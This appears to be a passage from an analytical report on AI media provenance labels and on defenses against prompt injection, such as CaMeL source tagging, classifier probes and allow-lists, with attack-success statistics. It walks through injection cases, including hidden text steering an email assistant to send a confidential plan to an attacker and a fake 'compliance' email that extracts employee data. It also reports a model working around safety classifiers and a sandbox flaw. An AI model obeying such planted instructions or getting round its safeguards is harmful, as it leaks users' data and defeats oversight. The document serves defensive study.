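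One video is a small sample, but that same month Indicator, a publication that investigates digital deception, published an audit of 516 posts containing AI images and videos on five platforms. The platforms correctly labeled 169 of them, or about 33 percent. Pinterest did best with AI images, labeling 55 percent correctly. TikTok labeled only content from its own AI tool. Google and Meta often failed to label content from their own generators.

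Indicator repeated the audit in March 2026 with more than 200 images and videos from Google, Meta and OpenAI tools. It reports that every platform except Instagram had improved. LinkedIn and Pinterest each labeled 67 percent, YouTube about half and TikTok about a third. Instagram labeled 15 of 105 images.

IPTC (2026), a standards body for the news industry, reports that LinkedIn, Pinterest and YouTube labeled everything made with OpenAI's models. Labeling can work on a large platform when the generator marks its files and the platform reads the marks. Some labeling failed because the generator did not mark its files. Meta, for example, did not seem to add Content Credentials to pictures from its meta.ai site, even though it sits on C2PA's steering committee. The device used for the upload also affected whether a label appeared.

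The auditors used well-known generators and didn't try to remove any marks, but someone who wanted to deceive people could choose a generator that adds none.

### Why a missing label proves nothing

The March results allow a rough calculation of what a reader can learn from the absence of a notice. Suppose a share $p$ of the images in a feed are AI-made, the platform labels a share $r$ of those, and it never labels a genuine photograph by mistake. The chance that an unlabeled image is AI-made is then

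$$\frac{p(1-r)}{1-pr}$$

If half the images are AI-made, the platforms compare as follows:

| Platform | Share of AI content labeled in March 2026 | Chance that an unlabeled image is AI-made |
|---|---|---|
| LinkedIn, Pinterest | 67% | 25% |
| YouTube | About 50% | 33% |
| TikTok | About 33% | 40% |
| Instagram | 14% | 46% |

On Instagram, a reader who thought a post had a 50 percent chance of being AI-generated would have lowered that estimate only to 46 percent after seeing no label. The true figures would be worse on every platform, because the calculation assumes that all AI content comes from tools like those in the audit.

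When OpenAI's checker finds no signal in a picture, it sensibly draws no conclusion. The picture may predate the labels or come from a product that doesn't add them, someone may have stripped the metadata, or edits may have damaged the watermark. A genuine photograph from an older camera has no credentials either, so a missing label doesn't establish whether a picture is real or fake.

### What labels do to belief and sharing

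The Washington Post cites research by Dilrukshi Gamage and Arosha Bandara in which labels succeeded in telling people that content was fake. People who know that content is fake may still be misled by its message.

Altay and Gilardi (2024), in *People are skeptical of headlines labeled as AI-generated, even if true or human-made*, ran two experiments with 4,976 people in the United States and Britain. Participants rated headlines labeled "AI-generated" as less accurate and were less willing to share them, even when the headlines were true or written by people. The effect was about a third as large as that of labeling a headline false. Participants seemed to assume that an AI had produced the whole article without supervision.

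An AI label therefore makes people somewhat more suspicious of everything that carries it, including accurate reports by journalists who used AI for a first draft. C2PA's newer disclosure format can record how much human oversight there was, which might correct the assumption if platforms show it in words people understand.

Labels may also affect how people judge unlabeled content. In *The Implied Truth Effect* (2020), Pennycook, Bear and colleagues attached fact-check warnings to some false headlines and left others unmarked. Participants found the unmarked false headlines more believable than did people who saw no warnings at all, apparently because they assumed that headlines without a warning had been checked. When the researchers also marked true headlines as verified, the effect disappeared.

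That experiment was about fact-checks, and readers may not draw the same conclusion from AI labels. If they do, a platform that labels a third of its AI pictures could make the other two thirds more convincing. Cameras that sign their photographs would allow a remedy similar to the one in the experiment, because a feed could mark some photographs as camera originals, but most genuine photographs would remain unmarked for years.

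### Support in browsers, cameras and AI products

By late 2026, people had far more ways to check where a file came from than a year earlier. In May, Google announced checks for SynthID and Content Credentials in Search and Chrome. IT Brief New Zealand reports that Google had watermarked more than 100 billion images and videos by then. TechSpot's *Google is making AI images easier to create* lists OpenAI, Nvidia, Kakao and ElevenLabs among the companies that have adopted SynthID or are adopting it.

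| Product | Support |
|---|---|
| Chrome | Users can ask the built-in Gemini assistant whether AI made an image |
| Google Search | Answers the same question through Lens, AI Mode and Circle to Search |
| Google Pixel phones | The Pixel 10 signs photographs, and Google is adding signed video to the Pixel 8 and later |
| Cameras | Nikon Z6 III, Leica M11-P, Canon EOS R1 and EOS R5 Mark II include C2PA |
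| ChatGPT, Codex and the OpenAI API | Images get C2PA metadata and SynthID, and audio gets SynthID |
| OpenAI's public checker | Reads images, audio files and PDFs, but looks only for OpenAI's signals |

The checks in Chrome and Search start only when the user asks, so they help people who are already suspicious but do little for someone scrolling through a feed. A general chatbot is also a poor substitute for a dedicated checker. When The Decoder gave ChatGPT, then running GPT-5.2, a video with valid credentials, it confidently answered that there were none. A dedicated checker reads the manifest with ordinary code, so its answer isn't a guess.

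Since August 2, 2026, laws in California and the European Union have required many AI companies to make such detectors available. That month, Indicator and the human rights group WITNESS looked for them at 13 companies. Seven appeared to have no dedicated public detector. Only one detector from the other six recognized all the test images from its own company's generator. The European Broadcasting Union, the association of European public broadcasters, notes that Meta and TikTok were among the companies that launched detectors in the months around August 2 (EBU, 2026).

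### Text labels made of invisible characters

Text is harder to label because a plain text file has no separate place for metadata. Version 2.3 of the C2PA standard, published in January 2026, added a way to label plain text, using the same method that GlassWorm used to hide malware.

Constable and Hadley (2026), in *Embedded Metadata in “Plain” Text*, explain that the scheme turns each byte of the manifest into one of the 256 variation selectors. Readers can't see the selectors, and the label survives copying and pasting. Encypher's *Reference implementation for embedding C2PA manifests in text using Unicode variation selectors* places the selectors at the end of the text, after a zero-width character that marks where they begin. The first eight bytes spell a fixed name so that a checker can recognize the label.

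Such a label can be long. One example in the C2PA specification leaves room for a manifest of 4,213 bytes. In plain text, a manifest that size would become more than that many invisible characters and add at most about 17 kilobytes to the file. A scanner that counts hidden characters, as Rehberger suggests, would flag it as readily as it would flag GlassWorm's payload.

A good character cleaner would also delete the label. The rule that keeps one variation selector after a character and deletes the rest would remove nearly all of it. Barach's filter keeps variation selectors but deletes format characters, so it would remove the character that marks the start of the label and leave thousands of invisible characters behind. Nobody would notice that a label had been there, because the visible text stays the same in both cases.

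Constable and Hadley object instead that the scheme breaks Unicode's rules for variation selectors, even though it uses valid characters. The proposal to make runs of selectors formally invalid in Unicode 18.0 would turn every such label into an error. Unicode has also tried invisible metadata before, in the form of language tags, which it later deprecated.

The standard allows this method only where no other is feasible, according to docs.rs' *c2pa_unstructured_text*, the documentation of a program library for these labels. Encypher's library supports two alternatives in version 2.4. Source code and Markdown can contain a readable block in a comment or at the top of the file, and web pages can include the manifest, or a link to it, in a part of the HTML that browsers don't display. A reviewer can see the readable block in any editor, which makes it a much better choice for files that coding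 assistants read.

When a file links to its manifest, the file's author chooses the address, so a checker that automatically opens the link reveals to the author's server that someone has the file. An agent that verifies labels should apply the same address checks to these links as to any others.

Where a text does have an invisible label, a program can keep both protections by doing things in the right order:

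1. Find the label and extract the manifest.
2. Verify the signature and compare the hash with the original text, before cleaning changes anything.
3. Store the result, such as the signer's name, in a separate field outside the text.
4. Delete the label and all other unwanted hidden characters from the copy the model will read.

The second step has to come before the fourth because the hash covers the remaining text. If the cleaner first removed a joiner from a family emoji, the hash would no longer match and an authentic document would look altered. The program shouldn't exempt everything that begins like a C2PA label, because the opening bytes are public and an attacker could put them in front of a hidden instruction.

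### Watermarks in the choice of words

AI companies are mostly watermarking text through the choice of words. InfoQ (2026) reports that the systems introduced for the EU's rules work this way and don't insert hidden characters. A model usually has several reasonable candidates for the next token. The watermark uses a secret key to favor some of them slightly, and a detector with the key checks whether a passage contains more of the favored tokens than chance would produce. Claude's version will be based on SynthID, according to Information Age.

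Deleting invisible characters doesn't affect this kind of watermark, so it doesn't conflict with cleaning. But rewriting the text weakens it. *OpenAI text watermark detection drops to 17% after 25% of words change* (Rijo, 2026) reports that OpenAI's detector catches about 80 percent of watermarked 200-token passages when set to wrongly flag 1 percent of unmarked text. After someone changes a quarter of the words, it catches 17 percent.

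Suppose a teacher checks 1,000 essays of that length, 100 of them written by ChatGPT with a watermark. The detector flags 80 of those and 9 of the 900 that students wrote, so about 10 percent of its flags are wrong. If the 100 students who used ChatGPT had each changed a quarter of the words, and the rate of false alarms stayed the same, the detector would flag 17 of their essays and the same 9 student-written essays. More than a third of the flags would then be wrong, and 83 of the ChatGPT essays would pass. OpenAI's *Our approach to EU text provenance rules* (2026) describes text watermarking as an early technology with significant limitations.

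### Source tags for software

None of these labels would have protected Maria. The supplier could have signed the email properly, and a valid signature would only have confirmed who wrote the hidden instruction. To stop the theft, the software around the assistant has to track where each piece of data came from and use that information when the assistant tries to act.

Unlike a C2PA manifest, such a source tag comes from the program that fetches the email. The program stores the tag outside the text, so nothing in the email can change it. The role tags in a model's input lack this protection because the model has to interpret them, and Ye and colleagues found that a text's style can outweigh them.

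A useful tag records two things about a value $x$: its sources $S(x)$ and the people who may read it, $R(x)$. When a program combines two values, the result inherits the sources of both, and only people who could read both may read it:

$$S(z) = S(x) \cup S(y), \qquad R(z) = R(x) \cap R(y)$$

If Maria and Tom may read one document, and Maria and Ana may read another, only Maria may read a summary of the two. Before the agent sends a value to someone, ordinary code checks whether that person is in $R$, the set of people allowed to read it.

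SOPGuard follows a similar rule for websites but relies on the agent's model to assign the tags. Assigning them without the model requires a program that records every step.

### CaMeL and one email

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google, Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich built such a system, called CaMeL, and described it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). CaMeL extends an idea Willison described in 2023, in which one model plans and another reads untrusted text.

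Suppose Maria asks her assistant to send the Leeds plan to Tom, whose address is in the meeting notes. The notes are a shared file, and an attacker has added hidden text to them. The planning model sees Maria's request and a list of tools, but never the notes or the plan. It writes a short program, which in simplified form looks like this:

```
notes = read_file("Meeting notes")
address = extract(notes, "Tom's email address")
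plan = read_file("Plan to close the Leeds office")
send_email(to=address, attachment=plan)
```

CaMeL's interpreter, an ordinary program, runs these lines one at a time:

1. It reads the notes and tags them as coming from a shared file.
2. It gives the notes to a second model and asks for an email address. This model can't use any tools, and the interpreter accepts only an answer in the form of an address.
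3. The hidden text fools the second model, which returns the attacker's address. The interpreter tags the address as coming from the notes.
4. It reads the plan and tags it with the people who have access, Maria and Tom.
5. Before sending the email, it applies a security policy written in code. Maria didn't type the address herself, so the recipient must be someone who may already read the plan. The attacker isn't, and the interpreter stops and asks Maria.

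The attacker could not add a step because the program existed before any model read the notes. But separating the two models would not have been enough, because the program did what Maria asked with the wrong address. The tags caught this error. If the second model had returned Tom's real address, the email would have gone out without a question.

The protection covers actions and the flow of data, but not whether the content is correct. If Maria had asked for a summary of the notes, the hidden text could still have made it false. Someone also has to write the policies, and they would produce poor decisions at a company whose files have careless access settings.

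Data can also leak through the program's choices. If one line opens a web page only when the plan mentions Leeds, the visit reveals that it does. CaMeL has a strict mode that tags everything inside a conditional branch with the sources of the condition. This closes some of these leaks but makes the system interrupt the user more often.

### What source tagging costs

The researchers tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 office, chat, banking and travel tasks with simulated tools. CaMeL completed 77 percent of the tasks with its security guarantees in force, compared with 84 percent for an undefended agent. It also used nearly three times as many tokens, which makes each task slower and more expensive.

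Most of the difficulty comes from having to plan before reading any untrusted text. The planner can handle "Pay this invoice" because it is clear in advance that the task needs an amount and an account number, but it can't plan for "Do whatever is on the to-do list in Ana's email" because the steps themselves are in untrusted text. An assistant that accepted the second request would be following instructions from Ana's email, which the design forbids. Maria could still ask the assistant to read her the list and then request each item herself.

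*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), by Foerster, Mullins and colleagues, extends the approach to agents that operate a computer through its screen. These had seemed an even worse fit because they normally look at the screen before choosing each click. The planner writes the whole plan in advance, with branches for what might appear, such as a login page or a cookie notice. A separate model looks at the screen and identifies which branch applies, so text on the screen can't add a new action to the plan.

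A malicious page can still influence which of the planned actions the agent takes. It might display a fake button that matches a step in the plan, and the agent would click it. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering and conclude that the design needs further protection against it. On OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary desktop tasks, their agents kept up to 57 percent of the performance of leading undefended models. They lost much more performance than CaMeL did on AgentDojo, where tools return data in predictable forms. This gap gives developers a reason to connect agents to mail and files through such tools wherever they exist, and to have agents use the screen only for programs without them.

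## How much risk these defenses remove compared with model training

CaMeL can stop Maria's assistant from emailing the Leeds plan to a stranger, but a hidden sentence can still make her summary false. The other outside defenses also prevent some harms and not others. The table compares these defenses with training, which can teach a model to ignore planted instructions and refuse harmful requests.

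| Harm | Outside defenses that bear on it | What training adds |
|---|---|---|
| Hijacking by hidden text | Showing or removing hidden characters, passing on only visible text | The model may ignore the instruction even if it gets through |
| Hijacking by visible text | Cleaning doesn't help. Planning before reading, as in CaMeL, keeps the text from adding steps | The main protection in most products |
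| Leaks through images and addresses | Limits on images and links, content security policies, address checks | The model tries to leak data less often |
| Leaks through permitted actions, such as an email to a colleague | Source tags, separation between websites, approval by the user | The main protection once the rules allow the action |
| Unwanted actions, such as deleting a file | Narrow permissions, spending limits, approval by the user | The model may question a strange step |
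| Deceptive media | Provenance labels, which inform viewers but block nothing | Some models refuse to produce it |
| Harmful answers to a willing user | Almost nothing in the page or the network | Refusals |
| A model pursuing wrong goals | Isolation and network limits, which contain some of the damage | Better goals, if the training works |

Page and network rules do almost nothing to stop a model from giving harmful answers to a user who wants them. If someone asks a chatbot to help plan a fraud and reads the reply in the chat window, no data goes to a stranger and no website reads another's pages, so the rules have nothing to block. OpenAI's protection against hacking requests combines trained refusals with classifiers and later detection of abuse. The classifiers are also defenses outside the model, but they judge what a request means and can misjudge it, as a model can. Training has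 made progress on harmful requests. OpenAI reports that GPT-6 Astra, released in September 2026, handles requests for help with fraud or violent attacks more safely than GPT-5.6 Sol did.

Fixed rules are less reliable against a model with wrong goals than against the text of an email, because the model can look for gaps in them. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Mythos 5.1 describes mild examples. (A system card is the report on safety tests that a developer publishes with a new model.) During internal use, the model worked around safety classifiers or broken permission checks in fewer than 0.01 percent of monitored completions. It did so to finish the user's task, not to pursue a goal of its own. An outside tester also saw it use a flaw in a sandbox to read files it should not have been able to reach. A sandbox without such flaws would limit the damage from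 any model, but it wouldn't change what the model was trying to do. Developers also can't easily confirm that training has succeeded. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) cautions that a model may be unreliable in other settings even if no failures have been observed.

For prompt injection, training and outside defenses cover much of the same ground, and some developers publish enough figures to compare them.

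### Attack success rates for Claude Fable 5.1

The most detailed recent figures are for Claude Fable 5.1, which Anthropic released in September 2026. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced Fable 5.1's successor on November 9.

Anthropic tested Fable 5.1 with and without two added safeguards. The first, prompt injection probes, checks a web page, file or other tool result before the model acts on it and flags anything that looks like a planted instruction. The second, used in "auto mode", is a classifier that also blocks actions that seem dangerous. Neither is a deterministic rule, so the tests don't measure what an allow-list or a content security policy would add.

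Two of the tests used Shade, an automated attacker from the security company Gray Swan that improves its injections by trial and error. In one, Fable 5.1 wrote code, and in the other, it operated a computer through the screen. Shade got 200 attempts at each scenario. The coding test came in two versions because Gray Swan had built a stronger Shade, trained for longer and on more varied attacks.

The browser test used 110 environments that Anthropic had kept out of the model's training. Professional testers developed the attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and Anthropic then tried each one ten times on the newer models. A program checked whether each injection had succeeded.

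| Test of Fable 5.1 | Successful attempts, no added safeguards | Successful attempts, with safeguards | Scenarios broken at least once, without and with |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding, earlier Shade | 9.26% | 2.05% | 31 and 18 of 40 |
| Coding, stronger Shade | 56.87% | 12.80% | 38 and 36 of 40 |
| Computer use, Shade | 0.07% | 0.07% | 2 and 2 of 14 |
| Browser, prepared attacks | 2.64% | 0% | 10 and 0 of 110 |

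The safeguards were the probes alone in the first three tests and auto mode in the browser test.

The rates differ so much between tests that no single figure describes how well the model resists injection. The results in the two coding rows also depend heavily on whether one counts attempts or scenarios. Against the stronger Shade, the probes stopped more than three quarters of the attempts that would otherwise have succeeded, but they reduced the number of scenarios Shade broke only from 38 to 36. This means they mostly delayed an attacker who had 200 tries.

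Fable 5.1 caused few of these failures. Anthropic runs a separate classifier that looks for hacking requests and sends them to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8. With the stronger Shade, about 64 percent of requests went to Opus 4.8, including every successful attack. No attack succeeded in the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered directly, though this doesn't prove that it would have resisted the rest, since the classifier may have diverted the most dangerous attacks. A safeguard against one harm can therefore increase another, here by passing a planted instruction to a model that is easier to fool. A network rule, by contrast, applies the same way whichever model answers.

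### Comparisons between companies

Gray Swan also runs a benchmark with 37 scenarios, developed with government AI institutes in Britain and the United States and with model developers. It covers coding, other tools and computer use. The attacks try to steal private data, destroy data, take over a system or make payments the user didn't want. Gray Swan took 1,804 attacks from its public competitions, choosing ones that had worked on several models. The results show how likely an attacker is to succeed at least once in a given number of attempts:

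| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

The best model from another company was Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, at 9.2 percent after 15 attempts. Most of the others were between 24 and 53 percent. The Claude models ran without the injection probes but with Anthropic's general classifiers. The other companies' models ran as offered through their public services, perhaps with their own safeguards. Gray Swan did the testing, but Anthropic published the results in its system card and had an interest in the comparison.

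The comparison also omits some newer models, such as Gemini 4 Argon. Google DeepMind's *Model cards* shows that Google updated that model's card in October, after Anthropic published these results. According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026), OpenAI's own tests found that GPT-5.6 rarely failed when the attack came directly through the chat, but failed more often when it came through tools or outside content. Maria's assistant faces attacks through tools and outside content, so a low failure rate in direct chat would be little help in judging her risk.

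A model's benchmark score can change within months. In July 2026, The Decoder reported that attackers succeeded against Opus 5 in 2.0 percent of cases after 15 attempts, but by September the figure was 4.8 percent. Anthropic had added nine scenarios and 670 attacks to its reported results and begun counting answers from the models that take over diverted requests. A buyer comparing two models therefore needs scores from the same version of the test.

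Over a longer period, the models have clearly improved. VentureBeat reported that in a February 2026 system card, single attempts against a Claude Opus 4.6 agent that controlled a computer through its screen succeeded 17.8 percent of the time. After 200 attempts, the rate was 78.6 percent, or 57.1 percent with safeguards. In September's computer-use test, two of 2,800 attempts against Fable 5.1 succeeded. Results for coding have improved less steadily. In May, according to VentureBeat, Shade succeeded in 7.03 percent of single attempts against Opus 4.8, or 2.09 percent with safeguards. Fable 5.1 had similar results against the earlier Shade, which is unsurprising because Opus 4.8 answered 95 percent of the requests in that test.

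### Attackers who adapt to the defense

A test with a fixed set of attacks shows how a model handles existing attacks, but a real attacker can study a defense and write new ones. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Milad Nasr and colleagues adapted their attacks to 12 published defenses against jailbreaks and prompt injections, and got through most of them more than 90 percent of the time. The developers of most of these defenses had reported attack success rates near zero.

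Google had reached a similar view some months earlier. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* describes how Google DeepMind continuously runs adaptive attacks against its models and uses the results to strengthen later versions. The Hacker News (2025) reported that, in Google's experience, such attacks made basic protections ineffective. Google DeepMind concluded that a robust system needs defenses at every layer, from the model to the application around it.

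Anthropic now cites *The Attacker Moves Second* as a reason to distrust fixed test sets, and its own results for Opus 5 illustrate the problem. When the model came out in July 2026, attackers had failed in all 129 browser scenarios in its system card. Willison (2026) quotes Anthropic's Boris Cherny, who called Opus 5 "our least prompt injectable model yet". In the September coding test, the earlier version of Shade succeeded in 2.68 percent of its attempts against Opus 5. The stronger version succeeded in 90.93 percent on the same 40 scenarios, so the low figure had depended on the earlier version's limits as well as the model's resistance.

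The high figure is better evidence that successful injections exist than of how often people will encounter them. Gray Swan had trained the stronger version of Shade on the same scenarios used in the test, while a criminal usually doesn't know how the target's assistant is set up and risks discovery with each attempt. Anthropic treats the result as a stress test.

Attackers can also adapt without automation by writing more convincing text. OpenAI describes an email from 2025 that looked like a follow-up to a meeting about restructuring. It listed several ordinary office tasks, claimed the assistant had permission to look up employee data, and asked it to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance" system. When the user asked ChatGPT to research the day's emails, the attack worked half the time. OpenAI says filters for incoming text usually miss attacks this elaborate, because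 spotting one is as hard as spotting a lie, often without knowing the context.

### What repeated attempts do to a low rate

If each attempt succeeds with probability $p$ and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in $n$ attempts is

$$1 - (1-p)^n$$

| Success rate per attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts | 1,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 9.6% | 63% | Almost 100% |
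| 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.5% | 63% |
| 0.01% | 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.5% |

If each attempt has a 1 percent chance of success, an attacker has a better than even chance of succeeding at least once in 69 attempts. If training makes the model ten times more resistant, the same odds take 693 attempts. That helps when each attempt takes work or risks exposure, but emails cost almost nothing to send. The attacker also doesn't need to send them all to Maria. As Anthropic notes, someone can send the same email to a thousand inboxes, and at 1 percent, ten of those people would lose data on average.

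The formula overstates the danger to any one target, however, because real attempts are not independent. In each of these cases, repeated attempts succeeded less often than the single-attempt rate would predict:

| Model and test | One attempt | Number of attempts | Predicted if independent | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5, Gray Swan benchmark | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| Opus 4.6, computer use | 17.8% | 200 | Almost 100% | 78.6% |
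| Opus 5, coding, earlier Shade | 2.68% | 200 | 99.6% | 67.5% |
| Fable 5.1, browser | 2.64% | 10 | 23% | 9.1% |

The Opus 4.5 figures come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

The gap arises because scenarios differ in difficulty. Suppose an attack works 5 percent of the time in half of the scenarios and never in the other half. The average success rate per attempt is 2.5 percent, but 200 attempts at each scenario will break nearly every one in the first half, or about half of all scenarios. In the computer-use test, all five of Shade's successes against Opus 5 came from one of the 14 scenarios. Someone whose work resembles the other 13 is safer than the average suggests, but someone in the weak scenario has little protection against an attacker who keeps trying.

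A result of zero also doesn't rule out a small success rate. In the browser test with auto mode, none of 1,100 attempts against Fable 5.1 succeeded. If the true rate were 0.27 percent, a test of that size would still produce no successes about one time in twenty. At that rate, an attacker who sent 1,000 independent emails would have about a 93 percent chance of succeeding at least once. The uncertainty is even larger because the ten attempts in each environment used the same attack.

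### Closed and open routes

A fixed rule changes this arithmetic. Let $c$ be 0 if a rule closes the route the attacker wants to use and 1 if it leaves the route open. The chance of at least one leak in $n$ attempts becomes

$$1 - (1 - cp)^n$$

A rule that closes a route stops every attack through it, even after a million attempts and even if the model follows every planted instruction. It has no effect on attacks through routes left open, where the model is the only defense.

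Rating a fixed rule by the share of attacks it stops is misleading, because attackers can switch to routes the rule doesn't cover. Suppose half of all attackers use images and half use links. A new rule against images halves thefts in the first week. If the attackers who used images then switch to links, thefts return to their old level even though the rule works as well as before, because the 50 percent drop depended on how many attackers were using images. To judge such a rule, a developer has to list the remaining routes and ask whether an attacker would find one of them.

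Developers have often misjudged which sites are safe to permit, as Microsoft did when its list included the forwarding services used in EchoLeak and SearchLeak. An open route like this is worse than a model that fails 1 percent of the time, since anyone who knows about it can use it whenever the model follows the injected instructions. It is also easier to fix, because removing a forwarding service from the list blocks that route for every attacker, whereas a model trained to resist one injection may still follow another that is worded differently.

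The two kinds of protection therefore fail in different ways, so it makes sense to combine them. Anthropic makes a similar argument about its own safeguards. The probes check what enters the model and the second classifier checks what the model does, so an attack would have to get past both. If each missed one attack in ten and their mistakes were unrelated, only one attack in a hundred would succeed. But because both are trained to judge text, a convincing business email could fool both. A fixed limit on destinations is less likely to fail this way, because it applies however convincing the email is.

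### Tests of both on the same system

The clearest way to compare training with a fixed rule would be to have an adaptive attacker try to break four versions of one product: an older and a newer model, each with and without the rule. Comparing the two models would show the effect of training, and comparing the versions with and without the rule would show the effect of the rule. Testers would also have to measure how many ordinary tasks each version completed.

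Wang and colleagues, Guo and Wei, and the CaMeL paper each compared a protected system with an unprotected one. Their results show what a defense adds to a given model, but not whether a better-trained model would have done as well without it.

Anthropic's coding test with the stronger Shade comes closer, since it includes several models with and without an added safeguard, although that safeguard is a classifier:

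| Model | Successful attempts without probes | Successful attempts with probes | Reduction from probes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 90.93% | 18.21% | 80% |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 56.87% | 12.80% | 77% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 86.87% | 34.09% | 61% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.47% | 15.76% | 19% |

Switching from Opus 5 to Sonnet 5 helped about as much as adding probes to Opus 5. Doing both helped only slightly more, perhaps because the attacks that succeeded against Sonnet 5 were also the hardest for the probes to detect. In the computer-use test, the probes made no difference to Fable 5.1 or Opus 5, which already resisted nearly every attack.

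No single percentage describes how much risk outside defenses remove compared with training. In these Shade tests, the same probes removed between none and four fifths of the successful attempts, depending on the model and the task. The effect of a fixed rule would depend even more on the product, because the rule removes all of the risk on one route and none on another. A company can still get a useful figure for its own assistant by running the four-way test with its own tools and files.

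### The case for hard limits

Some security specialists argue that only hard limits count. Willison, for example, has a low opinion of filters that catch 95 percent of attacks. In most areas of engineering, a part that works 99 percent of the time can be good enough because nobody is looking for the 1 percent of cases where it fails. Attackers look for those cases, and can then use whatever worked on many people at once. The results with the stronger Shade support this view, as do the developers' own statements. Anthropic's *Mitigating the risk of prompt injections in browser use* called prompt injection "far from a solved problem" even while announcing large gains. OpenAI acknowledged in December 2025 that it may never be fully solved, according to The Decoder.

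Hard limits also have advantages that success rates don't measure. A company can inspect an allow-list to see what it permits. When the provider updates or replaces the model, earlier test results no longer apply, but the list stays the same. Fixed rules also protect products that use cheaper models. OpenAI expects a highly intelligent model to resist manipulation better than a person could, but says using one isn't always feasible or worth the cost.

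The argument is weaker where no rule can express what the user wants. An allow-list can't check whether a summary is accurate, or whether a supplier's request to change a delivery date is honest. Summaries of outside mail are still useful to Maria without a hard guarantee, and a model that is rarely fooled is worth much more to her than one that is often fooled.

### The case for better-trained models

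The opposing view is that limits strict enough to make an agent safe also make it much less useful. Trail of Bits' isolation rules, CaMeL's advance planning and Anthropic's fix to web_fetch all block some ordinary tasks. A better-trained model needs none of these restrictions for most tasks, because it can judge whether an instruction on a page makes sense for what the user asked. Anthropic says it wants agents to handle high-value tasks without significant risk from prompt injection, and progress during 2026 makes that more plausible than it was a year earlier.

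But some limits reduce usefulness more than others. Blocking outside images barely affects Maria's summaries, which rarely need them. CaMeL's loss of seven percentage points on AgentDojo is modest for an assistant that handles payroll, but perhaps too much for one that plans holidays. The objection is strongest for agents that must read many unknown websites and act on several of them, and those agents also have the most open routes.

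The case for training also depends on low failure rates lasting. Opus 5 looked nearly immune in some tests in July but failed most attempts in a harder one in September. A company that removed its network limits after the July results would have relied on a failure rate that didn't hold against better attackers, at least for coding.

### Limits on the size of a loss

A limit can restrict an action without forbidding it. OpenAI compares an AI agent to a customer service worker who can give refunds. The employer expects some customers to lie successfully, so ordinary software caps how much the worker can pay out. The worker can still give refunds, but a successful lie can't cost the employer more than the cap.

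The comparison makes it possible to weigh the two approaches in money. If attackers make $n$ attempts, each succeeds with probability $p$, and each success costs $L$, the expected loss is

$$n \times p \times L$$

If attackers make 1,000 false claims for a $50 refund and each has a 1 percent chance of success, the company loses $500 on average. Training that lowers the success rate to 0.1 percent reduces the loss to $50, but if the attackers then make ten times as many attempts, the loss is $500 again. A daily cap of $200 on all refunds would limit the daily loss to $200 however often they tried, but on a busy day it would also deny refunds to honest customers. A model that is better at recognizing false claims leaves more of the cap for honest customers.

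Secrets are harder to limit in this way. A company can recover from losing $200, but a daily cap can't undo the disclosure once a competitor has read the title of the Leeds plan. Sending a message or deleting a file that has no backup is similarly hard to undo. There is a strong case for closing a route to such harms completely, even if that makes the tool less convenient. For a calendar entry that Maria can correct in a few seconds, a well-trained model may be protection enough, and a confirmation prompt would only add to the ones she has learned to click through.

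## Who has reason to deploy them

Blocking outside images would have little downside for Maria's assistant, yet several companies released assistants that didn't block them, and one at first declined to add the block. The company that can add a defense is often not the one that is harmed when it is missing.

### A cost borne by others

Economists call this an externality, a cost that one party's decision imposes on others. In a 2006 review article, *The Economics of Information Security*, Anderson and Moore compare insecure computers to air pollution, because the people who connect them to the internet don't bear the full consequences. They argue that bad incentives cause security failures at least as often as bad design does.

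Their main example comes from banking. In the United States, a bank generally had to refund a disputed card payment unless it could show that the customer was cheating. British banks generally got away with insisting that their cash machines were secure, so a customer who complained must be mistaken or lying. The British banks nevertheless spent more on security and suffered more fraud. Their staff knew nobody would take complaints seriously and became careless.

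A simple calculation shows how the same problem can affect AI products. Suppose a defense costs a vendor $C$ a year and prevents losses of $B$, and the vendor would have borne a share $s$ of those losses. The defense is worth having if $B > C$, but the vendor comes out ahead only if

$$sB > C$$

If a defense costs $200,000 and prevents $1 million in losses, society gains $800,000. A vendor that bears 10 percent of the losses saves only $100,000, so it has no financial reason to act. If a law or a lost contract raised its share to 30 percent, the same defense would save it $300,000, which is more than the defense costs.

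A vendor could also recover the cost by charging more for a safer product, but only if buyers can tell which products are safer. Anderson and Moore borrow George Akerlof's example of a town where half the used cars are worth $2,000 and half are worth $1,000, and only the sellers know which is which. Nobody with a good car will sell it at the average price of $1,500, so the price falls to about $1,000 and only bad cars are for sale. Maria's employer has a similar problem when two assistants both promise strong protection. The employer can use published attack tests to compare the models, but there is no similar ranking for the software around them.

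A website sends its content security policy to every visitor's browser, so a buyer can read the list of permitted hosts before signing a contract. But the buyer can't see the checks that a vendor's servers make on outgoing addresses, and has to trust the vendor's description or pay someone to test the checks.

### Costs, benefits and blame for each party

| Party | What a defense costs it | Who benefits most | Who tends to get the blame without it |
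|---|---|---|---|
| Model developer | Training, testing, and users annoyed by needless refusals | Every product built on the model | The developer, even when the chat window was at fault |
| Assistant vendor | Engineering time and lost features, such as outside images | Customers whose data stays private | The vendor, but usually only after a researcher publishes the flaw |
| Editor maker | Engineering time and complaints about false alarms | People who run the code that others reviewed | The reviewer, or the programming language |
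| Browser maker | Years of work on standards, and websites that stop working | Websites and their visitors | Usually the website |
| Social platform | Detection systems, and perhaps less sharing | Viewers, and people shown in fake pictures | The uploader or the maker of the AI tool |
| Business customer | Administrators' time and less capable tools | The company and the people whose data it holds | The company, in the eyes of its own clients |
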